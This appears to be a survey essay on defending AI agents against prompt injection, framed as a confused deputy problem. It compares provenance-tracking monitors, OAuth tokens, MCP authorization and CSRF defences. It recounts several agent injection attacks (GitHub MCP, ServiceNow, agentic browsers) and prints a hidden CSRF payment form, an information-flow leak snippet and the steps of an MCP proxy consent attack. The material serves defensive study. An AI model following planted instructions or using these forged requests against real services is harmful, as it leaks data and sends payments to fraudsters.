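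FIDES and CaMeL seem able to apply different requirements to different arguments of a call, contrary to Fan and colleagues' claim that they can only accept or refuse a whole call. Costa and colleagues describe a rule that requires a trusted recipient but allows an untrusted message, and Willison's example of a CaMeL rule checks only the recipient. PACT's contribution is to assign the roles automatically from a tool's description, so nobody has to write a rule for each tool.

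The assignment isn't always obvious. PACT treats an account as a destination, but an inflated amount can cost the company as much as a wrong account. If the amount may come from the email, something else has to limit it, such as a ceiling or a check against the purchase order.

PACT also has to work out where each value came from, since it monitors an agent whose model may have read everything. It looks for exact matches with earlier inputs, applies fixed rules, and leaves the remaining cases to a language model. On 20 real tools, it identified the source correctly 77.4% of the time. When the source is unclear, it chooses the less trusted one, so its mistakes should mostly block harmless calls. In AgentDojo tests with five models, it stopped every attack on the three strongest, which completed 38.1% to 46.4% of their tasks, 8 to 16 percentage points more than with CaMeL.

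Other monitors handle uncertain cases differently. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) treats a value with no identifiable source as hostile. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao's AgentCap rejects a payee only if every source for it is untrusted, so if a supplier's email repeats the account number the clerk typed, AgentCap does not reject the payee.

The record also has to last longer than one session. Suppose the assistant reads the fraudulent email on Monday and saves a note that Halvorsen has a new account. On Thursday the clerk asks it to pay Halvorsen, and it finds the account number in its notes. If it saved the text without the label, the number now looks like company data. Cai and colleagues describe the same pattern with a confidential forecast, which is stored in one session and copied into a report in a later one.

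### Checking at the last tool boundary

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) assumes a stronger attacker, who can also write tool descriptions. For example, a mail tool's code might always send whatever message the model supplies. A harmless description would tell the model to use a fixed template, while a malicious one would tell it to copy a password into the message. The code is the same in both cases, so inspecting it beforehand would not reveal the attack. PACE therefore decides whether to allow each call immediately before it runs, when its arguments are fixed.

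It makes two checks. The provenance check keeps a graph of which sources supplied which values. If untrusted or secret data could reach an unsafe effect, it looks for the lowest-weight set of links to cut, which in practice usually means blocking the call. The permission check compares the call's effects with what the user's request authorizes.

Li and colleagues tested the checks separately on 1,167 cases from several benchmarks, using the open model Qwen-3.8-27B. The table shows the results for AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, AgentDyn. The complete system also includes adjustments at the tool boundary that reduce needless refusals.

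| Checks in use | AgentDojo: attacks succeeding | AgentDojo: tasks completed | AgentDyn: attacks succeeding | AgentDyn: tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Provenance only | 0% | 13.6% | 0% | 0% |
| Permissions only | 0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Complete system | 0% | 67.2% | 0% | 33.3% |

Used alone, PACE's provenance check stopped attacks because it blocked almost everything. Most of PACE's useful protection came from its permission check, which resembles the limits on tool calls in Progent and AgentCap.

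PACE stays useful partly because the tested version can restore a call that the provenance check has blocked, as long as the permission check approves it. Li and colleagues prove guarantees for a stricter version that cannot restore blocked calls, but they did not test that version. The provenance check also misses secrets that the model has paraphrased, translated or split into pieces.

With PACE, the most successful group of attacks on the full AgentDojo benchmark worked between 0% and 8.1% of the time, depending on the model, and agents completed almost as many tasks as they did without it. In a small test, an attacker that adapted to the defence succeeded on none of 30 targets, compared with 21 against an unprotected agent. With so few targets, the true success rate could still be as high as 11%.

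### When only the email has the account

Now suppose the clerk writes, "Pay the attached invoice." The plan has to get the account from the email:

```python
mail = read_mail("Halvorsen Paper")
account = ask_reader("Which account should we pay?", mail)
amount = ask_reader("What is the amount due?", mail)
pay_invoice(account=account, amount=amount)
```

The account number is now untrusted, so a strict rule blocks the payment even if the invoice is genuine. More accurate tracking would not help, because the record already shows correctly that the number came from outside the company.

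Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, and FIDES blocks most of them by design. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with GPT-5.2. It completed 66.7% of them with its provenance rules off and 37.5% with them on. No attack succeeded with the rules on, in the runs that finished. (Li and colleagues report much weaker security for CaMeL, with up to 36% of attacks succeeding, on different models and a wider set of tasks.)

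Paying the attached invoice requires somebody to endorse the account number, and the endorsement is only as good as the reason for it. A good reason would be that ordinary code has found the same number in the company's supplier records. PACT allows for such checks, and a value that passes one gets a certificate for one role while keeping the record of its original source. A certificate for use as a payee's account therefore would not let the same text serve as a command.

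Garby and colleagues let the planner decide what to endorse. Their agent, Randori, runs in a small programming language they designed, which labels every value. The planner writes any endorsements into its plan before it sees outside data, so an email cannot cause it to add one. Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2. With Qwen3.7-plus, it completed 75% with endorsements and 62.5% without.

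Attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 runs, but most of those runs provide little evidence about endorsement, because in 873 of them the attack needed a tool call that the plan would never contain. Both successes were with GPT-5.2 on one task, in which the user asks the agent to read a text file and pay as it instructs, and the attacker has replaced the file's contents with his own payment request. Garby and colleagues tried this combination three times with each model, so it worked in two of three runs with GPT-5.2. Randori blocks the attack when endorsement is disabled.

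The planner endorsed the file only because the user had asked it to follow the file. Garby and colleagues think tracking can't address this attack, and the CaMeL paper puts the same case outside its threat model. That is a fair way to define the system's job, but users routinely ask for supplier invoices to be paid, and false invoices are a common kind of fraud. A company that uses such an agent for accounts payable needs another way to check the payee.

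The agent can also ask the user for the missing value. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) describes COBRA, a system that does this while it is still planning. In 20 of 22 tests where the request left out a critical value, COBRA asked the user before acting. The researchers then continued 11 such tasks with simulated answers. COBRA completed ten when the user supplied the value, but none when the user told it to use the record on file, because it stopped every time.

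COBRA turns "pay the attached invoice" into a request that names the account. If the clerk answers by copying the account number from the same email, the number becomes trusted even though nobody has checked it.

### Choosing a branch of the plan

Untrusted text can also affect a payment whose arguments are all trusted, as in the earlier case of an email that claims the finance director's approval. If the clerk makes the payment conditional on that approval, the plan contains a branch:

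```python
mail = read_mail("Halvorsen Paper")
approved = ask_reader("Has the finance director approved?", mail)  # yes or no
if approved:
    pay_invoice(account="4417", amount=2300)
```

FIDES has a rule for short answers that a company could use to allow such a plan. It records how much information a value can carry, ranking a yes-or-no answer below a choice from a list, and both below free text. A policy may then accept an untrusted yes or no in a consequential action because it carries only one bit. Costa and colleagues are right that a single bit is unlikely to deliver a prompt injection, since new instructions can't fit in it, but it is enough to release €2,300. The measure limits how many outcomes an attacker can choose between without accounting for the damage each could do.

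Labelling data as trusted can also hide an outsider's influence on a decision. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to change his password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the untrusted subject lines from the planner, but the planner treated a large amount as suspicious and changed the password. This broke no rule because Costa and colleagues had labelled amounts as trusted, even though anyone who sends a customer money chooses the amount.

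CaMeL does track conditions, but Garby and colleagues found a gap in how it does so. Their example concerns a secret bank balance:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > limit:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("outsider", "rich")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when a branch that depends on a secret changes it. If the secret balance is above the limit, `tmp` becomes false and secret, so the program skips the line that would change `rich`. `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is below the limit, `tmp` stays public, and `rich` becomes false without becoming secret. In both cases, `rich` is public and reveals whether the balance is above the limit. Presumably an untrusted condition could get past an integrity check in the same way. Garby and colleagues' own language is proved in Lean to prevent this kind of leak,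 but an endorsement still lets untrusted data through.

Branches matter even more for agents that operate a screen, because their planners cannot see a page in advance and have to provide for login forms, pop-ups and failed clicks. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) adapted CaMeL to such agents and counted about 40 branches in an average plan, compared with fewer than four on AgentDojo. They then attacked their own system by putting a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. Nearly every plan has a step for closing cookie notices, so the agent clicked the fake one and went to the attacker's site. In this attack, which they call branch steering, the agent never leaves its approved plan, but the attacker influences which part of it runs.

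In Zingrillo and colleagues' tests, branch steering and similar attacks succeeded in 65 of 74 cases against a system adapted from CaMeL and in 67 of 74 against an ordinary agent. The adapted system separates the planner from untrusted text but leaves out CaMeL's rules on data. The separation made almost no difference without those rules, but the tests did not cover CaMeL with the rules on.

COBRA attaches limits to each branch before the agent starts. For the branch that pays an invoice, the limits might specify the bank's web address, the permitted operation and the account number. Programs outside the model check every outgoing web request and tool call against the limits for the current branch. None of 199 attacks succeeded. Claude Sonnet 5 completed 38.8% of a set of ordinary computer tasks under COBRA and 51% without it, mainly because a planner that cannot see the screen has trouble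 predicting what will be on it.

A language model writes these limits from the user's request. Zingrillo and colleagues compared the limits with their own expectations in 30 cases and found 28 correct. Of the other two, one was too strict and one allowed an operation the user had not authorized.

If the user's permission depends on a fact that only untrusted text can supply, such as the director's approval, COBRA is supposed to ask the user before it settles the plan, because its limits don't establish whether a condition is true.

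Some tasks require the assistant to judge untrusted text and can't be reduced to extracting a single fact. If the clerk wants the assistant to choose the best of five suppliers' offers, the offers have to influence its choice. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) uses the term judgment manipulation for data that biases such a decision without posing as a command, and proposes that the decision should depend only on content relevant to the task. Provenance labels cannot enforce this, because an honest price and a misleading boast in the same offer come from the same supplier and carry the same label. The company can still restrict the choice to suppliers it has already approved, so that a manipulated decision leads to a worse deal rather than a payment to a stranger.

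## Acting with the caller's permissions

After Tymshare lost its billing records, its staff added a system call that let the compiler "switch hats". Each time it opened a file, the compiler could choose between its home files licence and the permissions of the user who had started it. It would ask to open the debugging output file with the user's permissions, or in Hardy's words, "by the authority vested in me by my invoker".

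This protected the billing file but did not generalise, because some of Tymshare's applications needed more than two authorities and files were not the only things that required permission. The changes were also scattered across the system. Somebody had to decide which authority each request should use, even in old code like the debugging routine, whose author had not faced that choice.

Later systems kept the idea that a deputy should use the caller's permissions. In an agent, the surrounding program has to select those permissions, because the model would choose based on text that an attacker can influence.

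### Unix programs and cloud services

In 1973 Bell Laboratories applied for a patent on Dennis Ritchie's method of letting a Unix program run with its owner's permissions instead of those of the user who starts it. Chen, Wagner and Dean, in *Setuid Demystified* (2002), explain how such a program switches between the two. Every running program has three user IDs. The real ID identifies the user who started it, the effective ID decides most access checks, and the saved ID keeps an earlier value so that the program can return to it. If Hardy's compiler had run on Unix, with 100 as the user's ID and 200 as the ID of the compiler's owner, it could have worked like this:

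| Stage | Real | Effective | Saved |
|---|---|---|---|
| Start | 100 | 200 | 200 |
| Writing debugging output | 100 | 100 | 200 |
| Writing statistics | 100 | 200 | 200 |
| After giving up the owner's permissions for good | 100 | 100 | 100 |

In the second row the compiler cannot open the billing file, because the system checks the permissions of user 100. But an attacker who takes over the program's code at that point can switch back to user 200, since the saved ID is still there. Only the state in the last row prevents that, but the compiler can then no longer write statistics.

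Programmers often got the switch wrong. On the Linux and Solaris versions that Chen and colleagues examined, calling `setuid(100)` at the start of this example changes only the effective ID. On FreeBSD it changes all three. A programmer who tested the call on FreeBSD might therefore assume that the program permanently gives up its owner's permissions, when on Linux it can still get them back.

A cloud vendor may act for thousands of customers, each with separate permissions. *The confused deputy problem*, from Amazon's cloud business AWS, describes a vendor called Example Corp that monitors its customers' AWS accounts. Each customer creates a role (a set of permissions in his own account), allows Example Corp to use it, and tells Example Corp the role's name. Role names are not secret, so a second customer can give Example Corp the first customer's role name and ask for a report on what he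 claims is his own account. AWS allows the request because Example Corp is permitted to use the role, and the second customer gets the first customer's data.

The remedy is an external ID. Example Corp assigns 12345 to the first customer and 67890 to the second, and the first customer adds a condition to his role that accepts only requests carrying 12345. If the second customer names the first customer's role, Example Corp's software attaches 67890, the number of the customer making the request, and AWS refuses. Example Corp has to choose the numbers itself, or the second customer could ask for 12345. It also has to authenticate its caller before it uses a role, as NCC Group's *Demystifying AWS’ AssumeRole and sts:ExternalId* (2019) points out. AWS relies on Example Corp to send the right number, so the condition doesn't protect customers if Example Corp is dishonest.

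AWS's own services need a similar condition. CloudTrail, which logs activity in an account, can write its logs to storage in another account. If the storage's owner accepts everything from CloudTrail, an outsider who knows the storage's name can direct his own logs there, much as the Tymshare user directed debugging output to BILL. The owner can prevent this by accepting CloudTrail's requests only when they carry a particular customer's account number, which AWS supplies.

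In both arrangements, ordinary software fills in whom the deputy is acting for, so a sentence in a customer's email cannot change it.

### On-behalf-of tokens

OAuth is the web's main standard for letting an application use a service on a user's behalf. The user logs in at an authorization server and approves the application, which OAuth calls the client. The server then issues an access token, which the client attaches to its requests.

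A client can also get a token in its own name. Auth0, which sells login software, points out that the service receiving such a token knows only which application is calling, even if a user started the request. The office assistant's shared database login has the same defect, and the sales employee could read everyone's salary because of it. With an on-behalf-of token, his request would go like this:

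1. The employee logs in to the assistant, which receives a token identifying him.
2. He asks for everyone's salary, and the model writes a call to `look_up_record`.
3. The program around the model sends his token to the authorization server and asks for a new one with which to call the personnel service on his behalf.
4. The personnel service reads his identity from the new token, finds that he has no right to see salaries, and refuses.

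When the tool runs with the employee's token, the salary request fails however the employee words it, even if the model makes the call. The model doesn't see or choose the token. The same call succeeds for a payroll clerk, so the company doesn't need a general rule against reading salaries. This would also have protected the records in Quarkslab's medical assistant, because patient 1's token gives no access to patient 2's record, whatever prompted the request.

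The protection depends on the program never falling back on its own login. Microsoft tells developers never to use an application's own permissions to call another service while acting for a user. Its on-behalf-of exchange passes on only permissions that users can delegate, not roles that belong to the application. According to Microsoft's *Agent OAuth flows*, AI agents with their own identities can use the same exchange once the user has consented.

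*OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, the standard for such exchanges by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, provides for both impersonation and delegation. With impersonation, the new token identifies only the user, so the personnel service cannot distinguish the employee from his assistant. With delegation, the token also identifies the assistant, so the service can log which agent made a call or apply stricter rules to agents. Descope, another seller of login software, explains that the client gets a delegation token by submitting a token for itself along with the user's. McGuinness (2026) writes in the draft standard *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* that existing specifications still don't represent delegation consistently.

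The deputy also has to identify the caller correctly. CX Today's *AppOmni Uncovers Agentic AI Security Vulnerability in ServiceNow’s API and Agents* describes a flaw of this kind in ServiceNow, whose software companies use for internal support. Some outside programs authenticated to ServiceNow with a fixed secret that belonged to the integration rather than to a person. A feature called auto-linking then matched the outside user to a ServiceNow account, and that user's actions ran with the account's permissions. If the feature picks the wrong account, every later permission check uses the wrong person's permissions.

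Some deputies exist to do things their callers cannot. Meta's support assistant served people who had lost access to their accounts and so could not log in to obtain a token. For these tasks the deputy needs its own authority, and ordinary code has to limit how that authority is used. For instance, if the sales employee may know the average salary in his department, a separate service could read the table and return only the average.

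### A proxy with one identity

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), in which a client inside the AI application calls tools offered by a server. Some servers are proxies for another company's service. MCP's security guidance describes a confused deputy attack on these proxies that doesn't require a language model.

Suppose a proxy connects AI applications to an online file store. The file store knows the proxy by one fixed client ID, whichever application is using it. The proxy lets any application register and gives each one an ID of its own. After a login, the proxy sends the user's browser to the application's redirect address with an authorization code, which the application exchanges for an access token. The attack then works as follows:

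1. The clerk connects his usual AI application through the proxy. The file store asks whether he trusts the proxy, he agrees, and the file store saves a cookie in his browser recording his consent.
2. An attacker registers an application with the proxy and gives a web address of his own as its redirect address.
3. The attacker sends the clerk a link that starts a login for this new application.
4. The clerk clicks the link, and the proxy forwards the request to the file store under its fixed client ID.
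5. The file store finds the cookie and skips its consent screen.
6. The proxy sends an authorization code to the attacker's address.
7. The attacker exchanges the code for a token to the proxy, and can now use the file store as the clerk.

The clerk had agreed to let the proxy act for him, and the proxy used that consent for an application he had never approved. The file store could not have detected this, because both applications reached it under the same client ID.

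To prevent this, the proxy must keep a list of the applications each user has approved and check it before forwarding a login. At step 4 the attacker's application is missing from the clerk's list, so the proxy has to show its own consent page. The page must show the application's name, the permissions it requests and the address that will receive the code. The clerk may still approve the application by mistake, but he now sees a request before the attack can succeed. If the proxy records his decision in a cookie, the cookie must apply only to that application, or the original flaw returns.

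The proxy must also compare the redirect address in each login request with the registered one, character for character. This stops a variant of the attack in which the attacker uses the ID of an application the clerk has already approved and changes only the address. On its own, it would not stop the present attack, because the attacker registered his own address. A random one-time value, like the anti-forgery tokens websites use, ties the returning browser to the clerk's consent. The proxy must not set this value until the clerk has approved, or a crafted link could skip the consent page.

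The newest revision of the protocol, from 28 July 2026, discourages open registration. Model Context Protocol (2026) announced that client metadata documents will replace it, although it still works for now. With these documents, an application's ID is a web address where it publishes its name and redirect addresses. An attacker can publish such a document on his own domain, so a proxy still has to ask for consent to each application. When the redirect address points to the user's own computer, the document also cannot prove which local program is listening. A malicious program could therefore present a well-known application's document and receive the code.

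### One token for one server

An attacker can misuse a legitimate token by presenting it to a server it wasn't issued for. Suppose an attacker controls the calendar server that the clerk's application connects to, and the application also connects to a separate mail server. If the mail server accepts any token issued by the company's authorization server, the attacker can take the token that the application sends to the calendar server and use it to read the clerk's mail.

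The RFC 8707 standard lets a client name the server it wants a token for. Model Context Protocol (2025) already required clients to do this in June 2025. In the current revision, Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires servers to reject any token not issued for them, so the mail server must reject a token issued for the calendar server.

The same rules forbid token passthrough, in which an MCP server forwards the client's token to the service behind it. Passthrough is a simple way to act with the caller's permissions, but the service may rely on a token check that the MCP server never made, and its logs may not show which program made the call. Anyone with a stolen token could also use the MCP server to extract data. An MCP server that calls another service must therefore obtain a separate token for it. With an on-behalf-of exchange, that token can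 still identify the user, so the service can check the user's permissions.

These rules do not apply to every deployment. Under Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), authorization is optional, and local servers that communicate with the client through standard input and output should take their credentials from the environment instead. Such a server may well use one stored credential for every call, which is ambient authority again.

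The July revision also removed sessions from the protocol. To keep data such as a shopping cart between calls, a server now gives the model a text handle, which the model sends back as an ordinary argument. The server must not treat possession of the handle as proof of identity. The guidance recommends storing the cart under both the handle and the user ID from the verified token, so that a stranger who learns the handle cannot open the cart. The check doesn't help if instructions in an email cause the clerk's agent to use the handle for another of his carts, because both carts belong to him.

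In *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, a review for the Agentic AI Foundation, Tabata (2026) finds no fundamentally new authorization concepts in this revision of MCP. The revision applies established OAuth practice to agents. That practice was designed to identify the user and application behind a request, and it does this well.

### When the permission is the user's own

In May 2025 the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated an attack that involved no identity failure. Its *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a user who had connected Claude Desktop to GitHub, where programmers store code in repositories. He had one public repository and several private ones. Anyone can post an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository, and the researchers posted one containing instructions for agents.

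The user then asked the agent to look at the open issues. The agent read the planted one, fetched information from the private repositories, and put it in a proposed change to the public repository, where anyone could read it. The proposed change included the names of private projects, the user's plan to move to South America, and his salary. The model was Claude Opus 4, then new, and later models resist planted text much better.

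The GitHub server had no bug. heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the agent could reach the private repositories because the server used the user's own account. An on-behalf-of token would have given the same result, since the user is allowed to read his private repositories and write to his public one. Per-client consent, exact redirect matching and audience binding would not have helped either, because the user had connected the right application to the right server.

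The fraudulent Halvorsen invoice gets through in the same way. A token for the clerk, used instead of the company's shared bank key, would confirm only that he may make payments. Siu and colleagues therefore distinguish between who may access a resource and whose instruction led to the action. Determining whose instruction it was requires a function that identifies which input the agent followed, and they do not claim that a perfect one can exist for a neural network.

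Using the caller's permissions can increase what an attacker gains, as AppOmni showed with ServiceNow's agents. A researcher created a user account that could write support tickets but not read other people's, and used it to put instructions for agents in a ticket. When an administrator asked an agent to categorize that ticket, the agent called a second agent, which copied the contents of a restricted ticket into the attacker's. Both agents ran with the administrator's permissions because the administrator had started the task. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on during the attack. The Hacker News (2025) reported that ServiceNow considered this intended behaviour and clarified its documentation.

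The copying would have failed if the agents had used the permissions of the ticket's author. But they would first have had to recognize that the author's text, not the administrator's request, had prompted the copying. A stricter rule could limit the agents to what both people may do, as Gallo's rule on shared authority would. After reading a ticket from a junior employee, an administrator's agent could then do only what that employee could do, which would make it nearly useless for administration.

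In SC Media's *After the identity fix*, Nik Kale proposes that the program around the model sign a record of the user's request and the operation it calls for, and send that record with every tool call. A tool refuses if the requested operation differs from the signed one, so an agent asked to summarize a PDF could not change a customer's email address. The check is only as exact as the signed operation, though. When the clerk asks the assistant to pay Halvorsen's invoice, the signed operation is a payment, and a payment to the fraudster matches it unless the record also includes the account. The program also has to work out from the user's request which operations he meant, as Progent does.

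### What narrower tokens reduce

Willison, in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, attributes the GitHub leak to a combination of private data, malicious instructions and a way to send data out. A token with fewer permissions can remove the first or the last of these. For a user who wants the agent to read the issues on his public repository, the choice of token determines what a planted issue can still achieve:

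| The token allows | What a planted issue could still cause through GitHub |
|---|---|
| Reading and writing all repositories | Publication of private data |
| Reading all repositories | Private data entering the model's context, but no publication on GitHub |
| Reading and writing the public repository | Unwanted changes to the public repository |
| Reading the public repository | A misleading answer to the user |

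The last token is enough for the task. The second token is less safe than it looks, because the agent may have another tool, such as `fetch_url`, that can send the data elsewhere.

Invariant Labs recommends a similar limit outside the token. Its sample rule, written for a product it sells, lets an agent use only one repository per session. That would have prevented the leak, but it also blocks legitimate work across repositories, such as copying a fix from one project to another. GitHub (2025) took a different approach, announcing in August that its MCP server would scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as passwords and access keys. Such a scanner can recognize an access key by its format, but it can't recognize a sentence about someone's salary that way.

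MCP's procedure tends to give clients broader tokens as a task proceeds. If a server does not specify which scopes a request needs, the client asks for every scope on the server's published list. When a later call needs more, the client requests a new token that covers both the old and new scopes. This saves the user from approving the same permissions repeatedly, but an agent that needed write access once may still have it when it later reads untrusted text.

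Shortening a token's life mainly helps against theft. Hartman's *Your AI Agent Is an Easily Confused Deputy* cites a March 2026 attack on LiteLLM, a program that routes requests to AI providers and stores the access keys for them. The attackers collected long-lived credentials affecting an estimated 500,000 corporate identities. Hartman proposes a broker that keeps such credentials away from agents and issues tokens that expire within seconds or minutes. Each token works only for the agent that received it, so a thief who copies one cannot use it.

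Hartman's example is an agent that reads performance data, queries a database, opens a support ticket and notifies the staff on call, requesting a separate token from the broker for each step. Hartman argues that if an injection misleads the agent while it reads the performance data, the attacker has only a read-only token that lasts less than a minute and can't reach the database because no database token exists yet. This holds for an attacker who has stolen the token, but one who is steering the agent can have it request the database token, and that request would match the expected sequence of steps. The broker would still refuse access to services outside the agent's policy and require a person's approval for riskier operations.

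## Defences against cross-site request forgery

Many websites identify a logged-in user with a cookie, a small piece of data that the browser stores and attaches to its requests to that site. The browser may attach the cookie even when another site's page caused the request. Cross-site request forgery (CSRF) is an attack that exploits this behaviour. In *Cross-Site Request Forgery*, Valsorda calls it a confused deputy attack that uses the ambient authority of the user's cookies.

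Websites can block CSRF by checking where a request came from. When an agent follows a stranger's instructions, its requests still come from the expected source, so they pass the same checks.

### A forged payment

Suppose the accounts clerk is logged in to the bank's website and opens a fraudster's page in another tab. As in an example from MDN's *Cross-site request forgery (CSRF)*, a reference page for web developers, the fraudster's page contains a hidden form:

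```html
<form action="https://bank.example/pay" method="POST">
  <input type="hidden" name="account" value="9035">
  <input type="hidden" name="amount" value="2300">
</form>
```

A script submits the form as soon as the page loads. The browser sends it to the bank with the clerk's cookie, and the bank pays €2,300 to account 9035. The fraudster never sees the cookie. MDN lists three conditions for the attack: the site changes something in response to a request, it relies only on cookies to recognise the user, and an attacker can predict every other value in the request.

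Barth, Jackson and Mitchell (2008) report in *Robust Defenses for Cross-Site Request Forgery* that an attacker could at the time get a domain, a certificate and a server to host a hostile page for about $10. With only the ability to post on a forum, an attacker could include an image whose address was a request to another site, but this worked only against sites that changed data in response to a GET request, the kind browsers use to fetch pages and images.

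Barth and colleagues also describe login CSRF, in which the hostile page logs the victim in to the attacker's account. A dishonest merchant could do this to a customer paying through PayPal. The customer would then add his credit card to the merchant's account, believing the account was his own.

### What each defence checks

The most popular defence in 2008 was a secret token. The bank puts an unpredictable value in a hidden field of its payment form and refuses any payment request without it. The fraudster's page can send requests to the bank, but the browser doesn't let it read the bank's pages, so the fraudster can't get the token.

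OWASP's *Cross-Site Request Forgery Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a widely used guide, describes a way to compute tokens so that the server doesn't have to store them. In simplified form, the token is

$$t = \mathrm{HMAC}(k,\; s \,\|\, r)$$

where $k$ is the server's secret key, $s$ identifies the user's session, $r$ is a random number sent along with the token, and $\|$ joins the two values. The server recomputes $t$ when the form comes back. The fraudster could log in himself and get a valid token, but it would not match the clerk's session.

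Developers have to add the token to every form and can leak it by mistake. Barth and colleagues found that one protection tool, NoForge, also added tokens to links to other sites, which let those sites forge requests.

A site can also check where a request came from, using headers that the browser sends. The Referer header contains the full address of the page that caused the request, so some networks remove it for privacy. Barth and colleagues bought 283,945 advertisement impressions to measure how often this happened. They estimated that a site requiring the header would block 3–11% of users on unencrypted connections, but at most 0.22% on encrypted ones. They proposed an Origin header that contains only the scheme, host and port, and browsers now send it.

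Browsers have since added Fetch Metadata, a group of headers that describe the context of a request. The most useful one here, `Sec-Fetch-Site`, records whether a request came from the same origin, another origin on the same site (such as a different subdomain), another site, or directly from the user (such as by opening a bookmark). Scripts on a page cannot change the header.

The SameSite setting controls whether the browser attaches a cookie to requests from other sites. With `Strict`, it never does. With `Lax`, it does when the user follows an ordinary link, but not when another site submits a payment form like the fraudster's. OWASP writes that Chrome made `Lax` the default in 2020 and that Firefox and Edge followed. Valsorda says this rollout mostly failed because it broke login systems, and that the defaults now in use do not prevent CSRF. A site should therefore choose the setting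 explicitly.

OWASP now presents Fetch Metadata as an alternative to tokens, with a fallback for old browsers. (Microdot's *Cross-Site Request Forgery (CSRF) Protection*, the documentation of a small web framework, dates this position to December 2025.) It treats SameSite as an extra layer, partly because the setting trusts every subdomain. Valsorda recommends this procedure, which the Go programming language includes in its standard library:

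1. Allow GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests, which should never change anything.
2. Allow the request if its Origin header exactly matches an entry on a list of trusted origins.
3. If `Sec-Fetch-Site` is present, allow requests from the same origin or directly from the user, and refuse all others.
4. If both headers are missing, allow the request, because it did not come from a modern browser.
5. Otherwise, allow the request only if the host in the Origin header matches the host that the request is addressed to.

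Checking the `Sec-Fetch-Site` header requires no changes to a site's forms. In *datasette PR #2689*, Willison (2026) describes replacing CSRF tokens with this check in Datasette, his data-publishing tool, because adding a token to every form was a nuisance.

### The same payment through an agent

Suppose the clerk uses a browser agent, which reads pages, clicks and types in the browser where he is logged in. He asks it to deal with the morning's invoices. A forged email in Halvorsen's name says to pay €2,300 to account 9035 on the bank's website. The agent opens the bank's payment page, fills in the form and submits it.

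| What the bank receives | From the fraudster's page | From the misled agent |
|---|---|---|
| Session cookie, without SameSite | Clerk's cookie | Clerk's cookie |
| Session cookie, with `Strict` | None, so the bank refuses | Clerk's cookie |
| Secret token | None, so the bank refuses | Correct token from the real form |
| Origin header | Fraudster's site, so the bank refuses | Bank's own site |
| `Sec-Fetch-Site` | Another site, so the bank refuses | Same origin |
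| Account and amount | Chosen by the fraudster | Chosen by the fraudster |

Once the agent loads the bank's payment page, the checks can no longer distinguish the fraudster from the clerk. The agent is using the real form, and the browser reports this correctly. The email affected only what the agent typed, which none of the checks examines. If the agent followed a link from the email, the `Strict` setting might cause a short delay, because the browser would withhold the cookie until the agent clicked on something within the bank's site.

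The office assistant sends payments through a program that attaches the company's bank key, so its request has neither browser header. Valsorda's procedure allows such requests because a hostile page can't make a browser attach a key the browser doesn't have. Allowing them is correct for CSRF, but the request can still contain the fraudster's account number.

*Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, by the security company Trail of Bits, reports attacks on several browsers with built-in agents. In one, a planted instruction made the agent open a service where the user was logged in, read private data there and send it out. The paper calls this "functionally identical to a CSRF attack", because the agent's requests automatically carried the user's cookies. But the agent also reads the response and can pass it on, while an ordinary CSRF attacker usually can't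 see the response to a forged request.

In this respect, a misled agent is closer to cross-site scripting (XSS), in which an attacker runs a script inside the honest site's page. The script can read the token and submit the form. Barth and colleagues leave XSS out of scope, and OWASP warns that it defeats every CSRF defence. An XSS flaw normally affects one site, but an agent may be logged in to many.

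Agents also give the forum poster much more power. In *Robust Defenses*, he can only cause GET requests. In *Mind the Web*, Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues (2025) needed only the ability to post comments or place advertisements, and wrote instructions that looked like help with the user's task. Their attacks on four agents, including OpenAI's Operator, succeeded 80–100% of the time, depending on the type of attack. The attacks included posting on social media as the user, which an agent does through the site's own form.

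One CSRF defence, accepting a login link only in the browser that requested it, does carry over to a browser agent. Trail of Bits reproduced login CSRF with a page that contained a login link for the attacker's account. When the user asked for a summary of the page, the agent opened the link and silently logged the user in as the attacker. Barth and colleagues had found a similar gap in the login system OpenID, which did not tie a login to the browser that started it. The defence would stop this attack, whoever opens the link, but it would not stop an agent from typing the attacker's password into the real login form.

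The other defences can also fail in ordinary web programs. OWASP describes client-side CSRF, in which a site's own script takes part of a request from a source that an attacker can influence, such as the end of a web address. The script then attaches the real token and sends the request from the correct origin. OWASP's remedies, which resemble the limits on tool calls, are to keep the attacker's input out of the request, check its values, or let it choose only from a list of safe requests.

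### Checking what the request contains

*The Agent Clicks Approve* (Hossen, 2026) tested browser agents on two kinds of form. In the first case, the user asked only for a summary of a page about a billing export. A two-sentence note on the page said the work could not continue until someone cleared an access review. The agent followed a link and pressed "Approve access", which gave an outside application access to the user's account. In the second case, the user asked the agent to complete any pending setup tasks listed in a guide. The guide contained an outsider's web address, and the agent registered it to receive the account's billing events.

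All 73 attacks succeeded against agents based on Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5. In 92 runs with a harmless note in place of the attack, the agents never submitted either form. Hossen's server required no login, so the experiment does not measure how a real service's defences would respond. But the agents used the service's own form, so they would have submitted any CSRF token it contained.

Hossen counts the billing-events runs as unauthorized because the user delegated the work without choosing where the events should go. This is debatable, since the user did ask the agent to follow the guide. An instruction to pay an attached invoice raises the same problem.

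Hossen also told Haiku that page text was untrusted and that only the user's task could authorize an approval. Seven of ten attacks on the approval form still succeeded. On another version of the pages, which labelled the parties and used OAuth terms, the same instruction reduced successful attacks to one in ten. A developer who tested only the labelled pages would have thought the instruction worked well.

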